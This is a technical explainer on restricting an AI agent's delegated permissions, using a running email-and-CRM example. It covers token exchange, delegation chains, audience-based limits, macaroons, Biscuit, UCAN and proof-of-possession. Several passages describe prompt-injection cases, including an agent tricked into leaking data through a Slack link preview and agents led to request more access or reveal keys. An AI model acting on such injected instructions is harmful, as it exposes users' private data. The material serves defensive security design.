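Signals can also arrive late or get lost, and a platform may be slow to apply them, as Exchange can be with changes to an app's permissions. It's safer to combine a signal, which can end access quickly, with a short expiry time in case the signal fails. For services in different organisations, Chen and colleagues ask for a stated limit on how old revocation information may be, so that a service can refuse requests when its information is too old.

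### Time, use and task limits for Maya

The new conditions fit around the earlier rules for senders, recipients and records:

```
TASK acme-renewal-17
  starts  when Maya gives the instruction
  ends    on Friday at 17:00 in Maya's time zone,
          or when Maya cancels it,
          or when the CRM shows that Acme has signed

Any request
  deny   if the task has ended

Read a message
  deny   if the mail service received it before 1 September

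Send a message
  deny   if its sending time is after Friday at 17:00
  deny   if the agent has already sent 20 messages in this task
  deny   if the agent has sent 5 messages in the past hour

Create, edit or delete a draft
  allow  if the draft is new or the agent created it in this task
```

The program checks the "deny" rules before the earlier ones, so they can only narrow what the agent may do. It checks the rule for drafts before the final rule that denies anything else. Maya has to choose the two message limits and the date in September herself because her instruction doesn't mention them.

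Suppose the agent asks at 16:58 on Friday for permission to write to a new person at Acme, and Maya approves at 17:05. The program still refuses to send the email, because it checks the task again before sending. The email scheduled for Monday also fails.

These rules can't erase what the agent has already read. If its software keeps Acme's emails in a log or in the model's saved memory, they will still be there on Saturday. Maya's company would need a separate rule requiring the agent's operator to delete them.

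## How could a permission show whom the agent acts for?

An agent can use Maya's identity, use its own identity while acting on her behalf, or act on authority of its own. The choice determines whose name goes into the log and whose limits the server applies. Suppose the agent opens Acme's CRM record at three in the morning:

| Arrangement | Log entry | Whose limits apply |
|---|---|---|
| Impersonation | Maya opened Acme's record | Maya's, narrowed by the token's scope and expiry |
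| Delegation | The renewal agent opened Acme's record for Maya | The part of Maya's access that she delegated, plus any rules for agents |
| Own authority | The renewal agent opened Acme's record | The agent's, even if Maya can't open the record herself |

*OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, by Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, defines impersonation and delegation. If the agent impersonates Maya, a server that receives its token can't distinguish the agent from her. If she delegates to the agent, it keeps a separate identity and the server can identify it as her representative.

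Impersonation works with software that wasn't built for agents, but Maya gets the blame for whatever the agent does. The CRM also can't apply a stricter rule to the agent than to her. Chen and colleagues find that OAuth has no standard way to mark a request as coming from an automated agent, so services have to infer it from unusual traffic or from the name the software reports. A token may identify the application that requested it, but this doesn't show whether Maya or the agent made the request, because she might use the same application to look up a record herself.

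A service's own AI features are another kind of caller. A subscriber to a database of research papers might allow its built-in summariser, but not an outside agent, to process her saved papers, or the reverse. Chen and colleagues point out that built-in features typically don't pass through the authorisation system, so she has nowhere to record a refusal.

An agent's own authority suits work it doesn't do for any particular user. In one of Chen and colleagues' examples, a security agent finds malware on an employee's laptop, ends his sessions, cuts the laptop off from the network and suspends his account. It would make no sense to run that agent with the employee's permissions. But if an agent with broad authority takes requests from many people, any of them can use it as a confused deputy, getting it to do things they aren't allowed to do themselves, unless something also checks the requester's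 permissions. The dedicated Salesforce user described earlier also has its own authority, so the administrator has to keep its access small.

### How token exchange records a delegation

Token exchange lets a program trade one token for another. It has been a Proposed Standard, a formal stage of IETF approval, since January 2020. To act for Maya at an imaginary CRM, the agent would do the following:

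1. It sends the CRM's authorisation server a token that represents Maya and a second token that represents the agent. It also states where it wants to use the new token and which scopes it needs.
2. The server checks both tokens and decides whether this agent may act for Maya. Her token can help by including a `may_act` claim that names the agent.
3. The server issues a new token that identifies both of them.

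Decoded and slightly simplified, the new token might look like this:

```
{
  "iss":   "https://login.crm.example",
  "aud":   "https://api.crm.example",
  "sub":   "maya@ourfirm.example",
  "scope": "records.read",
  "exp":   1791561600,
  "act":   { "sub": "renewal-agent" }
}
```

The `iss` claim names the server that issued the token, and `aud` names the server that should accept it. The `sub` claim identifies Maya, whose access the agent is using, and `act` identifies the agent. The token expires at 17:00 London time on Friday 9 October 2026.

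If the agent sends only Maya's token in step 1, the new token lets it impersonate her, not act as her delegate. Even if it also sends its own token, the server's policy determines whether the new token identifies the agent. A company that wants the agent's name in its logs therefore has to check that its authorisation server adds the `act` claim and that the CRM records it.

Cancelling Maya's original token doesn't necessarily cancel the new one. Jones and colleagues treat the exchange as a single event that creates no lasting link between the tokens, and they let each system decide whether cancelling the original also cancels the new one. The server should therefore make the new token expire quickly.

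### What happens when the agent uses another agent?

Suppose Ortiz asks for the renewal price, and Maya's agent passes the question to a second agent that specialises in looking up prices. The price agent exchanges the token it received for one of its own. These are the parts that change:

```
{
  "scope": "renewal-price.read",
  "exp":   1791536700,
  "act": {
    "sub": "price-agent",
    "act": { "sub": "renewal-agent" }
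  }
}
```

The outermost `act` claim identifies the agent making the request, and the one inside it identifies the previous agent. If the price agent called a third agent, the server would add another `act` claim. Maya remains the subject throughout. This record of who passed authority to whom is called the delegation chain.

The new token has a narrower scope and expires at 10:05 on Friday morning, so the price agent can read a price for a few minutes but can't open the rest of the record. The agent has no access to Maya's mail, so it couldn't follow a hidden instruction to forward her messages, even though the agent that called it can send mail.

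Token exchange allows this narrowing but doesn't guarantee it. Jones and colleagues suggest using scopes and short lifetimes to limit abuse, and leave the details to the authorisation server's policy. If the server checks only that Maya has the access the price agent requests, the price agent could obtain more access than the agent that called it. To prevent this, the server should compare each request with the token the agent is exchanging, and refuse any wider scope or later expiry.

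The standard also limits how the chain can be used to control access. A server deciding whether to allow a request must consider only the current actor and the token's main claims, and treat earlier actors as information only. So if the CRM follows the standard, it can't refuse the price agent on the grounds that an untrusted agent appears earlier in the chain. The authorisation server has to take account of the untrusted agent when it issues the token.

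Requiring permissions to narrow at every step can conflict with giving each agent only what it needs. Chen and colleagues describe an insurance claim that passes through four agents, which take in, verify, approve and pay the claim. They say the verifying agent should have no authority to pay. But if each agent could pass on only some of the permissions it held, the paying agent could never receive that authority through the verifying agent. The insurer could solve this by having a central server give each agent its own permissions, or by using tokens that let an agent pass on a permission it can't use itself.

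Chen and colleagues also say that no standard explains how to nest `act` claims into a chain that others can verify. The token exchange standard has included nesting since 2020, so their complaint is about verification. A server that receives the price agent's token has to trust the issuer's account of the chain. That may be fine inside one company, but a supplier that receives an order from an unfamiliar manufacturer's agent has little reason to trust the manufacturer's server. With an ordinary access token, the supplier can't check that each step narrowed the authority.

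Two proposals address parts of the problem. *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues, 2026) defines six ways to preserve and check a chain of actors, which differ in how much of the chain they disclose. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) proposes a consistent way to describe actors across several types of token. Both are individual drafts, so developers shouldn't expect other companies' servers to support them yet. Some other token formats let the receiver check the narrowing directly.

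### Cross App Access

In the examples so far, one authorisation server knows both Maya and the agent. In practice, Maya signs in through her company's identity provider, the service that handles employees' logins, while the CRM has a separate authorisation server. The agent usually connects to the CRM by sending Maya to a consent screen. SC Media, a cybersecurity news site, explains that the administrator's log at her company shows a routine sign-in but doesn't show the CRM giving the agent a token. Some applications show their administrators which agents have access, but most don't.

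Parecki, McGuinness and Campbell (2026), in *Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant*, route the connection through the identity provider. Okta, which sells such a service, markets the method as Cross App Access. Before anyone uses it, the administrator sets a policy that lets the agent act for certain employees at the CRM with certain scopes. The process is then:

1. Maya signs in to the agent's application through the identity provider, which gives the application a signed statement of who she is.
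2. The application returns the statement to the identity provider and asks for a grant to use at the CRM.
3. The identity provider checks the administrator's policy, removes any scopes that it doesn't allow, and returns a signed grant.
4. The application presents the grant to the CRM's authorisation server, which checks who issued it, that it is meant for this CRM, and that it names this application.
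5. The CRM's authorisation server applies its own policy. It can refuse, narrow the access further, or issue an access token for everything in the grant.

The administrator approves the connection, though the CRM can still refuse it. Maya only signs in. This saves her from a consent screen for every service, but she never approves this agent's access to this CRM.

The grant can specify a service and its scopes. It can also include the more detailed conditions of Rich Authorization Requests, but these work only if the CRM supports them. If the CRM's narrowest scope is "read records", the administrator can't use Cross App Access to limit the agent to Acme's records.

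The CRM also decides how long the access token lasts. In Parecki and colleagues' example of an AI agent, the grant lasts five minutes and the access token 24 hours. If the administrator withdrew his approval just after the CRM issued such a token, the agent could keep reading records for almost a day. SC Media calls the identity provider's lack of control over token lifetimes an unsolved problem.

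However, the draft advises the CRM not to issue a refresh token. Once the agent's access token and grant have both expired, the agent must return to the identity provider, which checks the current policy. Maya's company can enforce her Friday deadline there if the CRM issues short-lived tokens and the policy includes the deadline. Without such a policy, the agent may be able to use a refresh token from the identity provider to request new grants over the weekend while Maya is away.

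SC Media presents the lack of prompts as a security benefit. Many organisations grant broad access at the start to avoid interrupting users later. An agent using Cross App Access can instead start with a short-lived, read-only token and request more access when needed. But an agent that follows a hidden instruction can also request more access without Maya noticing. The administrator's policy then limits what the agent can get, and a policy written to cover every account manager's work will allow much more than Maya's task needs.

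The method also does not yet provide a full record of which agent acted. The grant identifies Maya and the application, and it may include an `act` claim, but the draft leaves later documents to define how the identity provider should check an agent's own token. Parecki and colleagues warn that without such a check, someone could combine a valid token for a user with an unrelated token for an agent and obtain a grant that overstates the agent's authority.

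Their document is a draft that an IETF working group has adopted. The version of 21 May 2026 expires on 22 November unless a new one replaces it. MCP has moved faster. Its version, Enterprise-Managed Authorization, became stable in June 2026, according to WorkOS's *Inside the ID-JAG* (2026). Model Context Protocol lists support in Anthropic's Claude and Microsoft's Visual Studio Code, and in services including Asana, Canva and Figma. The services it names include none of the four platforms compared earlier. Some listed services haven't finished their own versions. Atlassian, for example, described its support as a private beta.

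### Microsoft's agent identities

Microsoft's Entra Agent ID gives agents their own identities, but the type of permission shows whom an agent is acting for. With delegated permissions, it acts on behalf of a user, and with application permissions, it acts on its own authority. An administrator reviewing an agent therefore needs to check the type of each permission as well as the agent's name.

The identity also belongs to the agent rather than to a task. If Maya uses the same agent for Acme's renewal and another customer's complaint, the agent's name alone won't show which job led it to open a record. The company would have to log a task identifier as well.

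### Who will read the answer?

So far, the limits have depended on Maya and her agent. In a shared channel, other people see what the agent writes, and some of them may not have access to the data it used.

*When AI Agents Serve Shared Workspaces, Authorization Must Follow the Audience* (Kolhe, 2026) repeats an example from the OpenID Foundation. A chief financial officer adds an agent to a Slack channel and connects it with his own credentials. A junior analyst asks about the budget for pay, and the agent answers using files that include executives' salaries. Every access check passes because the officer is allowed to read those files, and the whole channel learns what the chief executive earns.

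Kolhe's solution is to find out who can read the channel before the agent retrieves anything, and to let it use only data that all of them may see. In mathematical terms, this is the intersection of their permissions. Suppose Maya asks her agent for an update on Acme in a channel with Leo from support and Priya from finance:

| Information about Acme | Maya | Leo | Priya | Agent may use it in the channel |
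|---|---|---|---|---|
| Renewal date | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Renewal price | Yes | No | Yes | No |
| Support tickets | Yes | Yes | No | No |
| Lowest price the company would accept | Yes | No | No | No |

Maya could get all four items in a private conversation, but here the agent can give her only the date. Because it never retrieves the other three, it can't reveal them by mistake or in response to a hidden instruction. Filtering the finished answer would be less reliable, since the filter would have to recognise a price however the agent phrased it.

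Kolhe doesn't discuss how much less useful this makes the agent. Adding a member to the channel can only reduce what the agent may use. If Leo left, the agent could discuss the price again. In a channel of 20 people who could each read a random 90% of the company's records, only about 12% of the records would be open to everyone in the channel (0.9^20 ≈ 0.12). Real colleagues' permissions overlap more, but one contractor with very little access could still make the agent almost useless. The agent could remain more useful by posting the date in the channel and sending Maya the rest privately.

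The list of readers can also change after the agent answers. Someone who joins the channel next week may be able to scroll back and read an answer that was safe when the agent wrote it.

Kolhe also overstates how many attacks the intersection would stop. He cites four serious vulnerabilities from 2025 as examples of systems that didn't check who would receive the data. In one, an attacker could make an agent put private data into a web link in Slack, and Slack would send the data to the attacker's server when it fetched a preview. Comparing the channel members' permissions wouldn't have prevented that, because the attacker's server wasn't a member. The software would have to check every destination, including links. In another, an attacker who knew a ServiceNow user's email address could impersonate that user, so a check on the recipient's permissions would have passed. Kolhe works for Okta,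 which published the same article with a section on the products it sells for computing intersections.

The rule doesn't work for Maya's emails to Acme either. Ortiz has no CRM account, so she and Maya have no permissions in common, and the agent couldn't tell her the price of her own renewal. Permission to open a record is different from permission to be told something in it. For people outside the company, someone has to list what the agent may disclose. Maya could use the four renewal fields as that list, if she is happy for Acme to see all of them.

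### Identity and audience limits for Maya

These conditions can be added to the earlier rules:

```
Any request
  deny   unless the token's subject is Maya
  deny   unless the current actor is renewal-agent or price-agent
  deny   if Maya may not do this herself
  deny   if the actor is price-agent, unless it is reading
         Acme's renewal price

Post in a shared channel
  deny   if any member may not read all the data in the answer
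  ask    otherwise
```

To apply the channel rule, the program has to determine which data the agent used. It can list the records and fields the agent has read during the task and treat the answer as if it may contain any of them. If the agent has already looked up the price to write an email to Ortiz, this is stricter than Kolhe's approach, because the program would block even a post that gave only the renewal date, since Leo may not see the price. Maya could avoid that by having a separate agent, with no memory of the emails, answer questions in the channel.

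## Which credential formats can carry these limits?

Several token formats can carry almost all of Maya's limits, but a limit in a token has no effect unless the server that receives the token checks it. Suppose her agent's token has a field that limits it to writing to Ortiz. If the mail service ignores that field and checks only the scope, "send mail", it will deliver an email from the agent to a competitor. Whichever format the token uses, the provider has to define the condition and write the code that tests it.

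The formats differ mainly in who can add conditions. In OAuth, the authorisation server decides what goes into a token. Macaroons, Biscuit and UCAN allow attenuation, which means that whoever holds a credential can make a narrower copy without contacting a server, and the recipient can't widen it.

### Rich Authorization Requests

*OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests* (Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell, 2023) adds a parameter called `authorization_details` to OAuth. An app can send this parameter wherever it would otherwise send scopes. The parameter holds a list of objects in JSON, a common text format for structured data. In the paper's main example, an object describes a bank payment of €123.50, with the payee's name and account number. The customer sees those details on the consent screen, so she approves only that payment.

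Every object needs a `type`, which determines what else it may contain. The standard (RFC 9396) also offers five common fields that the designers of any programming interface, or API, can reuse:

- `locations`: the servers where the permission applies
- `actions`: what the app may do, such as "read"
- `datatypes`: kinds of data, such as "contacts"
- `identifier`: one particular resource, such as a record
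- `privileges`: levels of access, such as "admin".

An object grants every combination of the values it lists. If it lists the actions "read" and "write" and the data types "contacts" and "photos", it grants all four combinations. An app that only needs to read contacts and write photos has to send two objects.

None of the common fields covers recipients, deadlines or DMARC results, so each API's designers must define fields for these in a type of their own. They also decide what the common fields mean, so "write" may include reading in one API but not in another. The authorisation server must refuse any request that contains an unknown type, or a known type with an unknown field. This is safer than ignoring a condition the server doesn't recognise, but it means Maya's agent can't make up a field for her deadline.

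A server can publish the names of the types it supports, but the standard has no format for describing them. Zehavi (2026) proposes one in *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling*, so that an app could look up a type's definition instead of relying on prior arrangements. This would help agents that encounter unfamiliar services, but the proposal is still an individual draft.

After Maya consents, the authorisation server has to pass the approved details to the resource server. It can put them inside a signed token, or keep them and let the resource server look them up. Either way, the resource server needs code that compares the details with the request. Chen and colleagues find no common way to tie constraints that a user approved earlier to an agent's later action, or to verify that the action complies.

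An app can also send scopes and detailed permissions together, which helps developers move gradually from one to the other. But if Maya's token contains both "send mail" and a list of recipients, a server that checks only the scope will ignore the list. Lodderstedt and colleagues recommend that each API use only one of the two.

### Maya's permission in OAuth

Suppose Maya's mail provider had defined a type for tasks like hers. Her agent could request the mail permissions like this, with two addresses standing in for everyone at Acme she had already corresponded with:

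```
[
  {
    "type": "https://mail.example/agent-task",
    "task": "acme-renewal-17",
    "ends": "2026-10-09T17:00:00+01:00",
    "actions": ["read"],
    "senders": ["ortiz@acme.example",
                "purchasing@acme.example"],
    "received_since": "2026-09-01T00:00:00+01:00",
    "dmarc_not_passed": "ask"
  },
  {
    "type": "https://mail.example/agent-task",
    "task": "acme-renewal-17",
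    "ends": "2026-10-09T17:00:00+01:00",
    "actions": ["send"],
    "recipients": ["ortiz@acme.example",
                   "purchasing@acme.example"],
    "other_recipients": {"acme.example": "ask"},
    "attachments": false,
    "max_sent": {"task": 20, "hour": 5}
  },
  {
    "type": "https://mail.example/agent-task",
    "task": "acme-renewal-17",
    "ends": "2026-10-09T17:00:00+01:00",
    "actions": ["create_draft", "edit_draft", "delete_draft"],
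    "drafts": "created_in_task"
  }
]
```

The CRM and the company's chat service have their own authorisation servers, so the agent would send each of them a separate request:

```
[
  {
    "type": "https://crm.example/agent-task",
    "task": "acme-renewal-17",
    "ends": "2026-10-09T17:00:00+01:00",
    "actions": ["read", "search"],
    "identifier": "account-4471",
    "fields": ["name", "renewal_date",
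               "renewal_price", "contract_length"]
  }
]

[
  {
    "type": "https://chat.example/agent-task",
    "task": "acme-renewal-17",
    "ends": "2026-10-09T17:00:00+01:00",
    "actions": ["post"],
    "readers": "may_read_all_data_used",
    "approval": "ask"
  }
]
```

The tokens would name Maya and the agent in the `sub` and `act` claims described earlier. Each authorisation server can use the `ends` field to store the deadline with Maya's grant, so that the deadline also applies to refreshed tokens.

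Some of these conditions are hard for the services to check. The chat service has no record of which CRM fields the agent used in its answer, so it can't apply the rule about readers on its own. The mail service can't check whether Maya has cancelled task 17 unless her company sends it that information.

Maya's agent may also not know that Acme's record is `account-4471`. The standard lets the agent leave out such a value so that the user can choose it during consent. Maya could pick Acme from a list, and the authorisation server would add the identifier to the details and return them with the token.

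If the price agent needs a token, the CRM's authorisation server can issue one that allows only reading `renewal_price`. The server must first confirm that this is narrower than the original permission, but Lodderstedt and colleagues explain that there is no standard way to compare permissions, so it needs separate code for each permission type. Sharma and colleagues' objection about values that an agent computes during a task also applies to these fields.

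### How macaroons add conditions

*Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) describes a credential to which its holder can add conditions, called caveats. A macaroon consists of an identifier, a list of caveats and a signature. The service that issued the macaroon allows a request only if every caveat is true.

The signature uses HMAC, a function that takes a secret key and a message and returns a short value. Anyone who knows the key can recompute the value, but without the key it isn't feasible to produce the right value for a new message or to work out the key from values already seen.

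The mail service chooses a secret key and calculates a chain, in which each result becomes the key for the next step:

```
sig0 = HMAC(key,  id)
sig1 = HMAC(sig0, caveat1)
sig2 = HMAC(sig1, caveat2)
```

The macaroon contains the identifier, both caveats and `sig2`, but not the key or the earlier signatures. When an agent presents it, the mail service uses the identifier to find the key, recomputes the chain of signatures and compares the last one with `sig2`. It then checks whether the request satisfies the caveats.

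Suppose Maya's company holds a macaroon with one caveat, `action = read`, and the signature `sig1`. To limit the agent to Ortiz's messages, the company adds the caveat `from = ortiz@acme.example` and calculates `sig2`, using `sig1` as the key. It gives the agent the identifier, both caveats and `sig2`, without having to contact the mail service.

The agent could add a third caveat in the same way, using `sig2` as the key. But it can't remove the second, because a macaroon with only the first caveat needs the signature `sig1`, and the agent can't calculate `sig1` from `sig2`. If it changes "ortiz" to another name, the mail service will calculate a different `sig2` and reject the macaroon. Adding `from = anyone` doesn't help either, because the caveat about Ortiz must still be true.

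This works only if the agent never had the broader macaroon. If the company gives it the original and asks it to make a narrow copy for itself, the agent can keep using the original. The company should therefore narrow the macaroon before handing it over. The agent can then safely make a still narrower copy for the price agent.

### How can another service check a condition?

A macaroon can also require proof from a service other than the one that issued it. This is a third-party caveat. Maya's company could use one to make the mail service reject requests after she cancels the task, even though the mail provider has no connection to the company's task records:

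1. The company's software creates a random key. It encrypts the key, together with the condition "acme-renewal-17 is open", so that only the company's task service can read them.
2. It encrypts a second copy of the key using the macaroon's current signature. The mail service can recalculate that signature and so decrypt this copy.
3. It adds both encrypted values to the macaroon as one caveat and calculates the next signature from them.
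4. The agent sends the task service its encrypted value. If the task is open, the task service returns a discharge macaroon, whose signature chain starts from the random key. It can add its own caveat, such as an expiry time one minute away.
5. The agent combines the two macaroons' signatures to tie the discharge to the original, and sends both macaroons with its request.
6. The mail service decrypts its copy of the random key and uses it to verify the discharge.

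Without step 5, a malicious service that the agent sent a request to by mistake could reuse the discharge to meet the same requirement in a macaroon of its own.

If Maya cancels the task, the task service stops issuing discharges, and the agent loses access when its last discharge expires. The mail service has to support macaroons, but it doesn't need any information about what the task service checked, or even which service did the checking.

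Birgisson and colleagues built a small image-sharing website to measure the delay. Checking a macaroon with four caveats added an average of 470 microseconds to a request. A login check through a third-party caveat added about three milliseconds, but part of the user's browser supplied the proof. A check by Maya's task service would take longer because it would also involve a network connection.

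### Maya's permission in macaroons

A caveat is either true or false, so it can't return "ask". The company can get the same result with two mail macaroons. One covers routine requests, and the other requires a discharge showing that Maya approved the request. In the real macaroons, Acme's addresses would replace `ACME_PEOPLE`:

```
MAIL: caveats in both macaroons
  1  actor = renewal-agent
  2  now < 2026-10-09T17:00:00+01:00
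  3  action is read, send, create_draft, edit_draft
     or delete_draft
  4  if reading: received since 2026-09-01T00:00:00+01:00
  5  if sending: no attachment,
                 sending time <= 2026-10-09T17:00:00+01:00,
                 fewer than 20 sent in acme-renewal-17,
                 fewer than 5 sent in the past hour
  6  if editing or deleting a draft: the agent created it
                                     in acme-renewal-17
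  7  third party, task service: acme-renewal-17 is open

MAIL: routine macaroon adds
  8  if reading: From is in ACME_PEOPLE and DMARC passed
  9  if sending: every recipient is in ACME_PEOPLE

MAIL: approval macaroon adds
  8  if reading: From is in ACME_PEOPLE
  9  if sending: every recipient is at acme.example
 10  third party, approval service: Maya approves this request

CRM
  1  actor = renewal-agent or price-agent
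  2  now < 2026-10-09T17:00:00+01:00
  3  action = read or search
  4  every record = account-4471
  5  every field is name, renewal_date, renewal_price
     or contract_length
  6  if actor = price-agent: action = read and
                             every field = renewal_price
  7  third party, task service: acme-renewal-17 is open

CHAT
  1  actor = renewal-agent
  2  now < 2026-10-09T17:00:00+01:00
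  3  action = post
  4  every reader may see all the data used
  5  third party, task service: acme-renewal-17 is open
  6  third party, approval service: Maya approves this request
```

Each service records that it issued its macaroon to Maya, and checks her own access as well as the caveats.

If Maya approves an email to a new person in Acme's legal department, the agent shouldn't be able to reuse her approval for a different email. The approval service can add a caveat to its discharge that lists the recipients and includes a cryptographic fingerprint of the text. The mail service then has to check that the message matches both before sending it.

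The mail service must also count sent messages by task. If it kept a separate count for each signature, the agent could add a meaningless caveat, get a new signature and send another 20.

The CRM has its own macaroon because each service verifies macaroons with a secret key that only it should know. Anyone with that key can also create macaroons without caveats.

Macaroons have no ready-made way to write "every recipient". Birgisson and colleagues let each service decide what its caveats mean, although they suggest a shared library for common ones such as expiry times. Madden (2024) gives the lack of a standard as a reason not to use macaroons. An agent that works with two mail providers might need to learn two sets of caveats.

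### Biscuit

Biscuit also supports narrowing a token offline, but it uses public-key signatures. A server can verify a token with the issuer's public key but can't use that key to create new tokens. This suits a provider whose mail, calendar and file servers all need to check the same token.

According to Biscuit's documentation, a token consists of blocks, and each block's signature covers its content and the public key for the next block. The token also includes the private key that matches the public key in the last block, so its holder can sign one more block. The holder replaces that private key with a new one before passing the token on. The recipient can't remove the new block because it doesn't have the old private key, which it would need to use the shorter token.

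Birgisson and colleagues considered a public-key version of macaroons but found it too slow for wide use. Creating an RSA key pair took 54 milliseconds on their server, while computing an HMAC-SHA-256 took about three microseconds. Biscuit uses newer kinds of keys that are much quicker to create, so those figures are a poor guide to its speed.

Biscuit also has a language for conditions. Clever Cloud's *Biscuit, the foundation for your authorization systems* (2021) explains that developers who use macaroons have to design their own way to write and test caveats. Biscuit adapts Datalog, a language that draws conclusions from facts and rules. Two of Maya's limits might look like this:

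```
check if time($now), $now < 2026-10-09T16:00:00Z;

check all recipient($address),
  ["ortiz@acme.example", "purchasing@acme.example"]
    .contains($address);
```

The time is 16:00 because Biscuit's example uses UTC, which is an hour behind London in early October. In the second rule, `check all` requires every recipient to be on the list, whereas `check if` would require only one match.

The mail service still has to supply the facts. If it leaves out the Bcc addresses, even a correctly written rule won't check them.

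### UCAN

In UCAN (User-Controlled Authorization Network), each delegation names the giver and the receiver by their cryptographic keys. The receiver signs each request it makes and can sign a narrower delegation to someone else. The server can follow the chain of delegations from the resource's owner to the last agent and check that no step widened the permission. The supplier in the earlier example could make this check with UCAN, but not with an ordinary access token.

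*Delegated Authority Evaluations v1.0 Preview* (Zagidulin and Caballero, 2026), a working-group draft on delegation to agents, describes how the narrowing works. Commands form a hierarchy, so permission for `/crud` includes `/crud/read` but not `/stack/pop`. A delegation is valid only while every delegation above it is valid. If Maya's delegation to her agent ends on Friday at 17:00, the agent can't give the price agent access that lasts until Saturday.

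UCAN also has a small policy language for further conditions. UCAN keys don't show who is responsible for an agent, so Maya's company would need a separate record linking each key to a person or organisation.

Zagidulin and Caballero call it an anti-pattern to forbid an agent to delegate further, because the agent could still make requests on another agent's behalf or share its key, and the server wouldn't see the delegation. If Maya lets her agent sign a narrower delegation instead, there is at least a record of it.

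### GNAP and transaction tokens

The IETF published the Grant Negotiation and Authorization Protocol (GNAP) as RFC 9635 in 2024. It is an alternative to OAuth with detailed permissions built in from the start. An app describes the access it wants in JSON, using common fields much like those above, and can keep negotiating with the authorisation server. If Ortiz brings in a colleague, Maya's agent could ask to add him to the existing grant. By default, each token works only with a particular key. Each API must still define what its permissions mean.

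Transaction tokens, which the IETF is still drafting, protect the details of a request as it moves between services inside one organisation. When Maya's agent asks the mail provider to email Ortiz, the request may pass through several internal services. The provider could put Ortiz's address into a short-lived signed token at the start, and the service that delivers the email could check that nobody had changed the address. The token would stay inside the provider's systems. It could help the provider enforce Maya's permission, but her agent would still need the credential that grants that permission.

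### What if someone steals the token?

Macaroons and Biscuits are bearer tokens, like ordinary OAuth tokens, so anyone who steals one can use it within its limits. A sender-constrained token works only if the program presenting it proves that it holds a particular key. "Sender" here means that program, not the author of an email, such as Ortiz.

The usual method in OAuth is DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession), defined in RFC 9449. The agent's application creates a private key and a matching public key, and the authorisation server ties the token to the public key. For each request, the application uses the private key to sign a small proof that includes the request's method and web address. A thief who has only the token can't produce a valid proof.

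The DPoP proof does not cover the recipient of an email. In the simplified mail request shown at the start, the URL path is `/messages/send` for every email, and the recipient is in the body. DPoP therefore can't enforce "write to nobody new" or detect a changed recipient. Zagidulin and Caballero describe a newer agent system, KYA-OS, whose signatures do cover the body. Neither DPoP nor KYA-OS stops a prompt injection, because the agent's own software will sign the resulting request.

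An agent might also follow an instruction to reveal its private key. Zagidulin and Caballero recommend keeping the key in a separate, more predictable program that signs requests for the agent. That program can't determine whether a request fits Maya's task unless it also checks her conditions.

Binding a credential to a key can let an agent pass on authority that it can't use itself. In the insurance example, the verifying agent could carry a payment token that works only with the paying agent's key. Madden lists `cnf`, the standard OAuth claim for naming a key, as a possible macaroon caveat. The caveat `actor = price-agent` needs a similar proof of a key, because otherwise any program could claim to be the price agent.

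OAuth's current security guidance recommends sender-constrained tokens but doesn't require them. According to Zagidulin and Caballero, most deployments still issue plain bearer tokens.

### How the formats compare

The table covers the formats that could carry the main conditions of Maya's permission. GNAP resembles Rich Authorization Requests in most of these respects.

| | Rich Authorization Requests | Macaroons | Biscuit | UCAN |
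|---|---|---|---|---|
| Narrowing offline | No, the authorisation server issues a new token | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Ending access early | Revoke the grant or token | List revoked tokens at the service, or stop issuing discharges | List revoked tokens where the servers can find it | Send a revocation to the server |
| What adds to the size | All the details, unless the token only refers to them | The text of each caveat | The text, a signature and a key for each block | A signed delegation for each step |
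| Who can read the conditions | The servers, and usually the agent | The holder and the service, except for encrypted third-party conditions | Anyone with the token | Anyone with the chain |

Offline narrowing lets Maya's agent hand a ten-second job to the price agent without waiting for an authorisation server. But cancelling that job early still requires a connection. Zagidulin and Caballero find that every system they surveyed needs one for revocation. Biscuit, for example, gives each token an identifier that can be added to a list of revoked tokens, but developers must store and distribute the list themselves.

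Maya's mail permission above takes about 700 characters in JSON without spaces, and about a third more in a signed token. If she listed 200 contacts as both senders and recipients, the addresses alone might take 10,000 characters. Many web servers reject request headers that long. The mail service could instead store a fixed copy of the list when Maya gives her instruction and put a short reference to it in the token.

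A reference also hides the addresses from anyone who finds the token. The limits can be confidential, for example if they show that Maya is negotiating with Acme. In OAuth, the initial request normally passes through the browser, so details in its web address could leak into histories and logs. Lodderstedt and colleagues suggest sending the details directly to the authorisation server and giving the browser only a reference. They also warn that encrypting the details may not be enough, because an attacker could submit the encrypted request from their own device and read the details on the consent screen.

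UCAN has the opposite problem, because every agent that uses a chain can see all the earlier delegations. Zagidulin and Caballero suggest creating a new key for each delegation, so that outsiders can't connect one chain with another. This hides the parties' identities but not what the delegations permit.

All four formats exist outside research papers, though support varies. Rich Authorization Requests were designed with banking and electronic signatures in mind and have been a Proposed Standard since May 2023. Security Boulevard's *Cloud Series* (2020) describes macaroons as a type of OAuth token available in a commercial identity service. The Eclipse Foundation, which hosts open-source projects, lists Biscuit 6.0.0 as a June 2025 release. The database company Space and Time uses Biscuit to control access to individual tables, according to its *About Biscuit Authorization*. The storage service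 Storacha uses UCAN, though UCAN's implementation guide still describes version 1.0 as a release candidate.

The Gmail, Microsoft 365, Salesforce and HubSpot permissions described earlier don't use any of these formats to carry conditions like Maya's. Her company could still give the agent a macaroon or Biscuit that works only at the company's own gateway. The gateway would check Maya's conditions and then use the platform's broader token, which the agent would never hold.

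## Where can the limits be checked?

Maya's company could check her agent's requests in four places: inside the agent's program, in the MCP server or other tool it calls, in a gateway, or at the platform that holds the data. Checks closer to the agent can use more information about the task, but checks closer to the data are harder to bypass.

Where a limit should be checked also depends on what has gone wrong. A hidden instruction may mislead the model while the program around it still works properly. In a worse case, an attacker controls the program and can use every credential it holds.

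| Place | What a check there can inspect | Who can bypass it | What a compromised agent could still do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent's program | Maya's instruction, every tool call and everything the agent has read | Anyone who controls the program or gets hold of its token | Anything the token allows, if an attacker controls the program |
| MCP server | The tool, its arguments and the caller's token | An agent with another route to the same data; whoever runs the server | Misuse the operations the server permits, or use tools elsewhere |
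| Gateway | Calls to all the tools behind it | An agent with a direct token or a browser signed in as Maya; whoever runs the gateway | Send permitted people anything it has read |
| Platform | Every request to that platform, and the stored data | An administrator who can change the rules; the platform's own staff | Send permitted people anything it has read, including data from other platforms |

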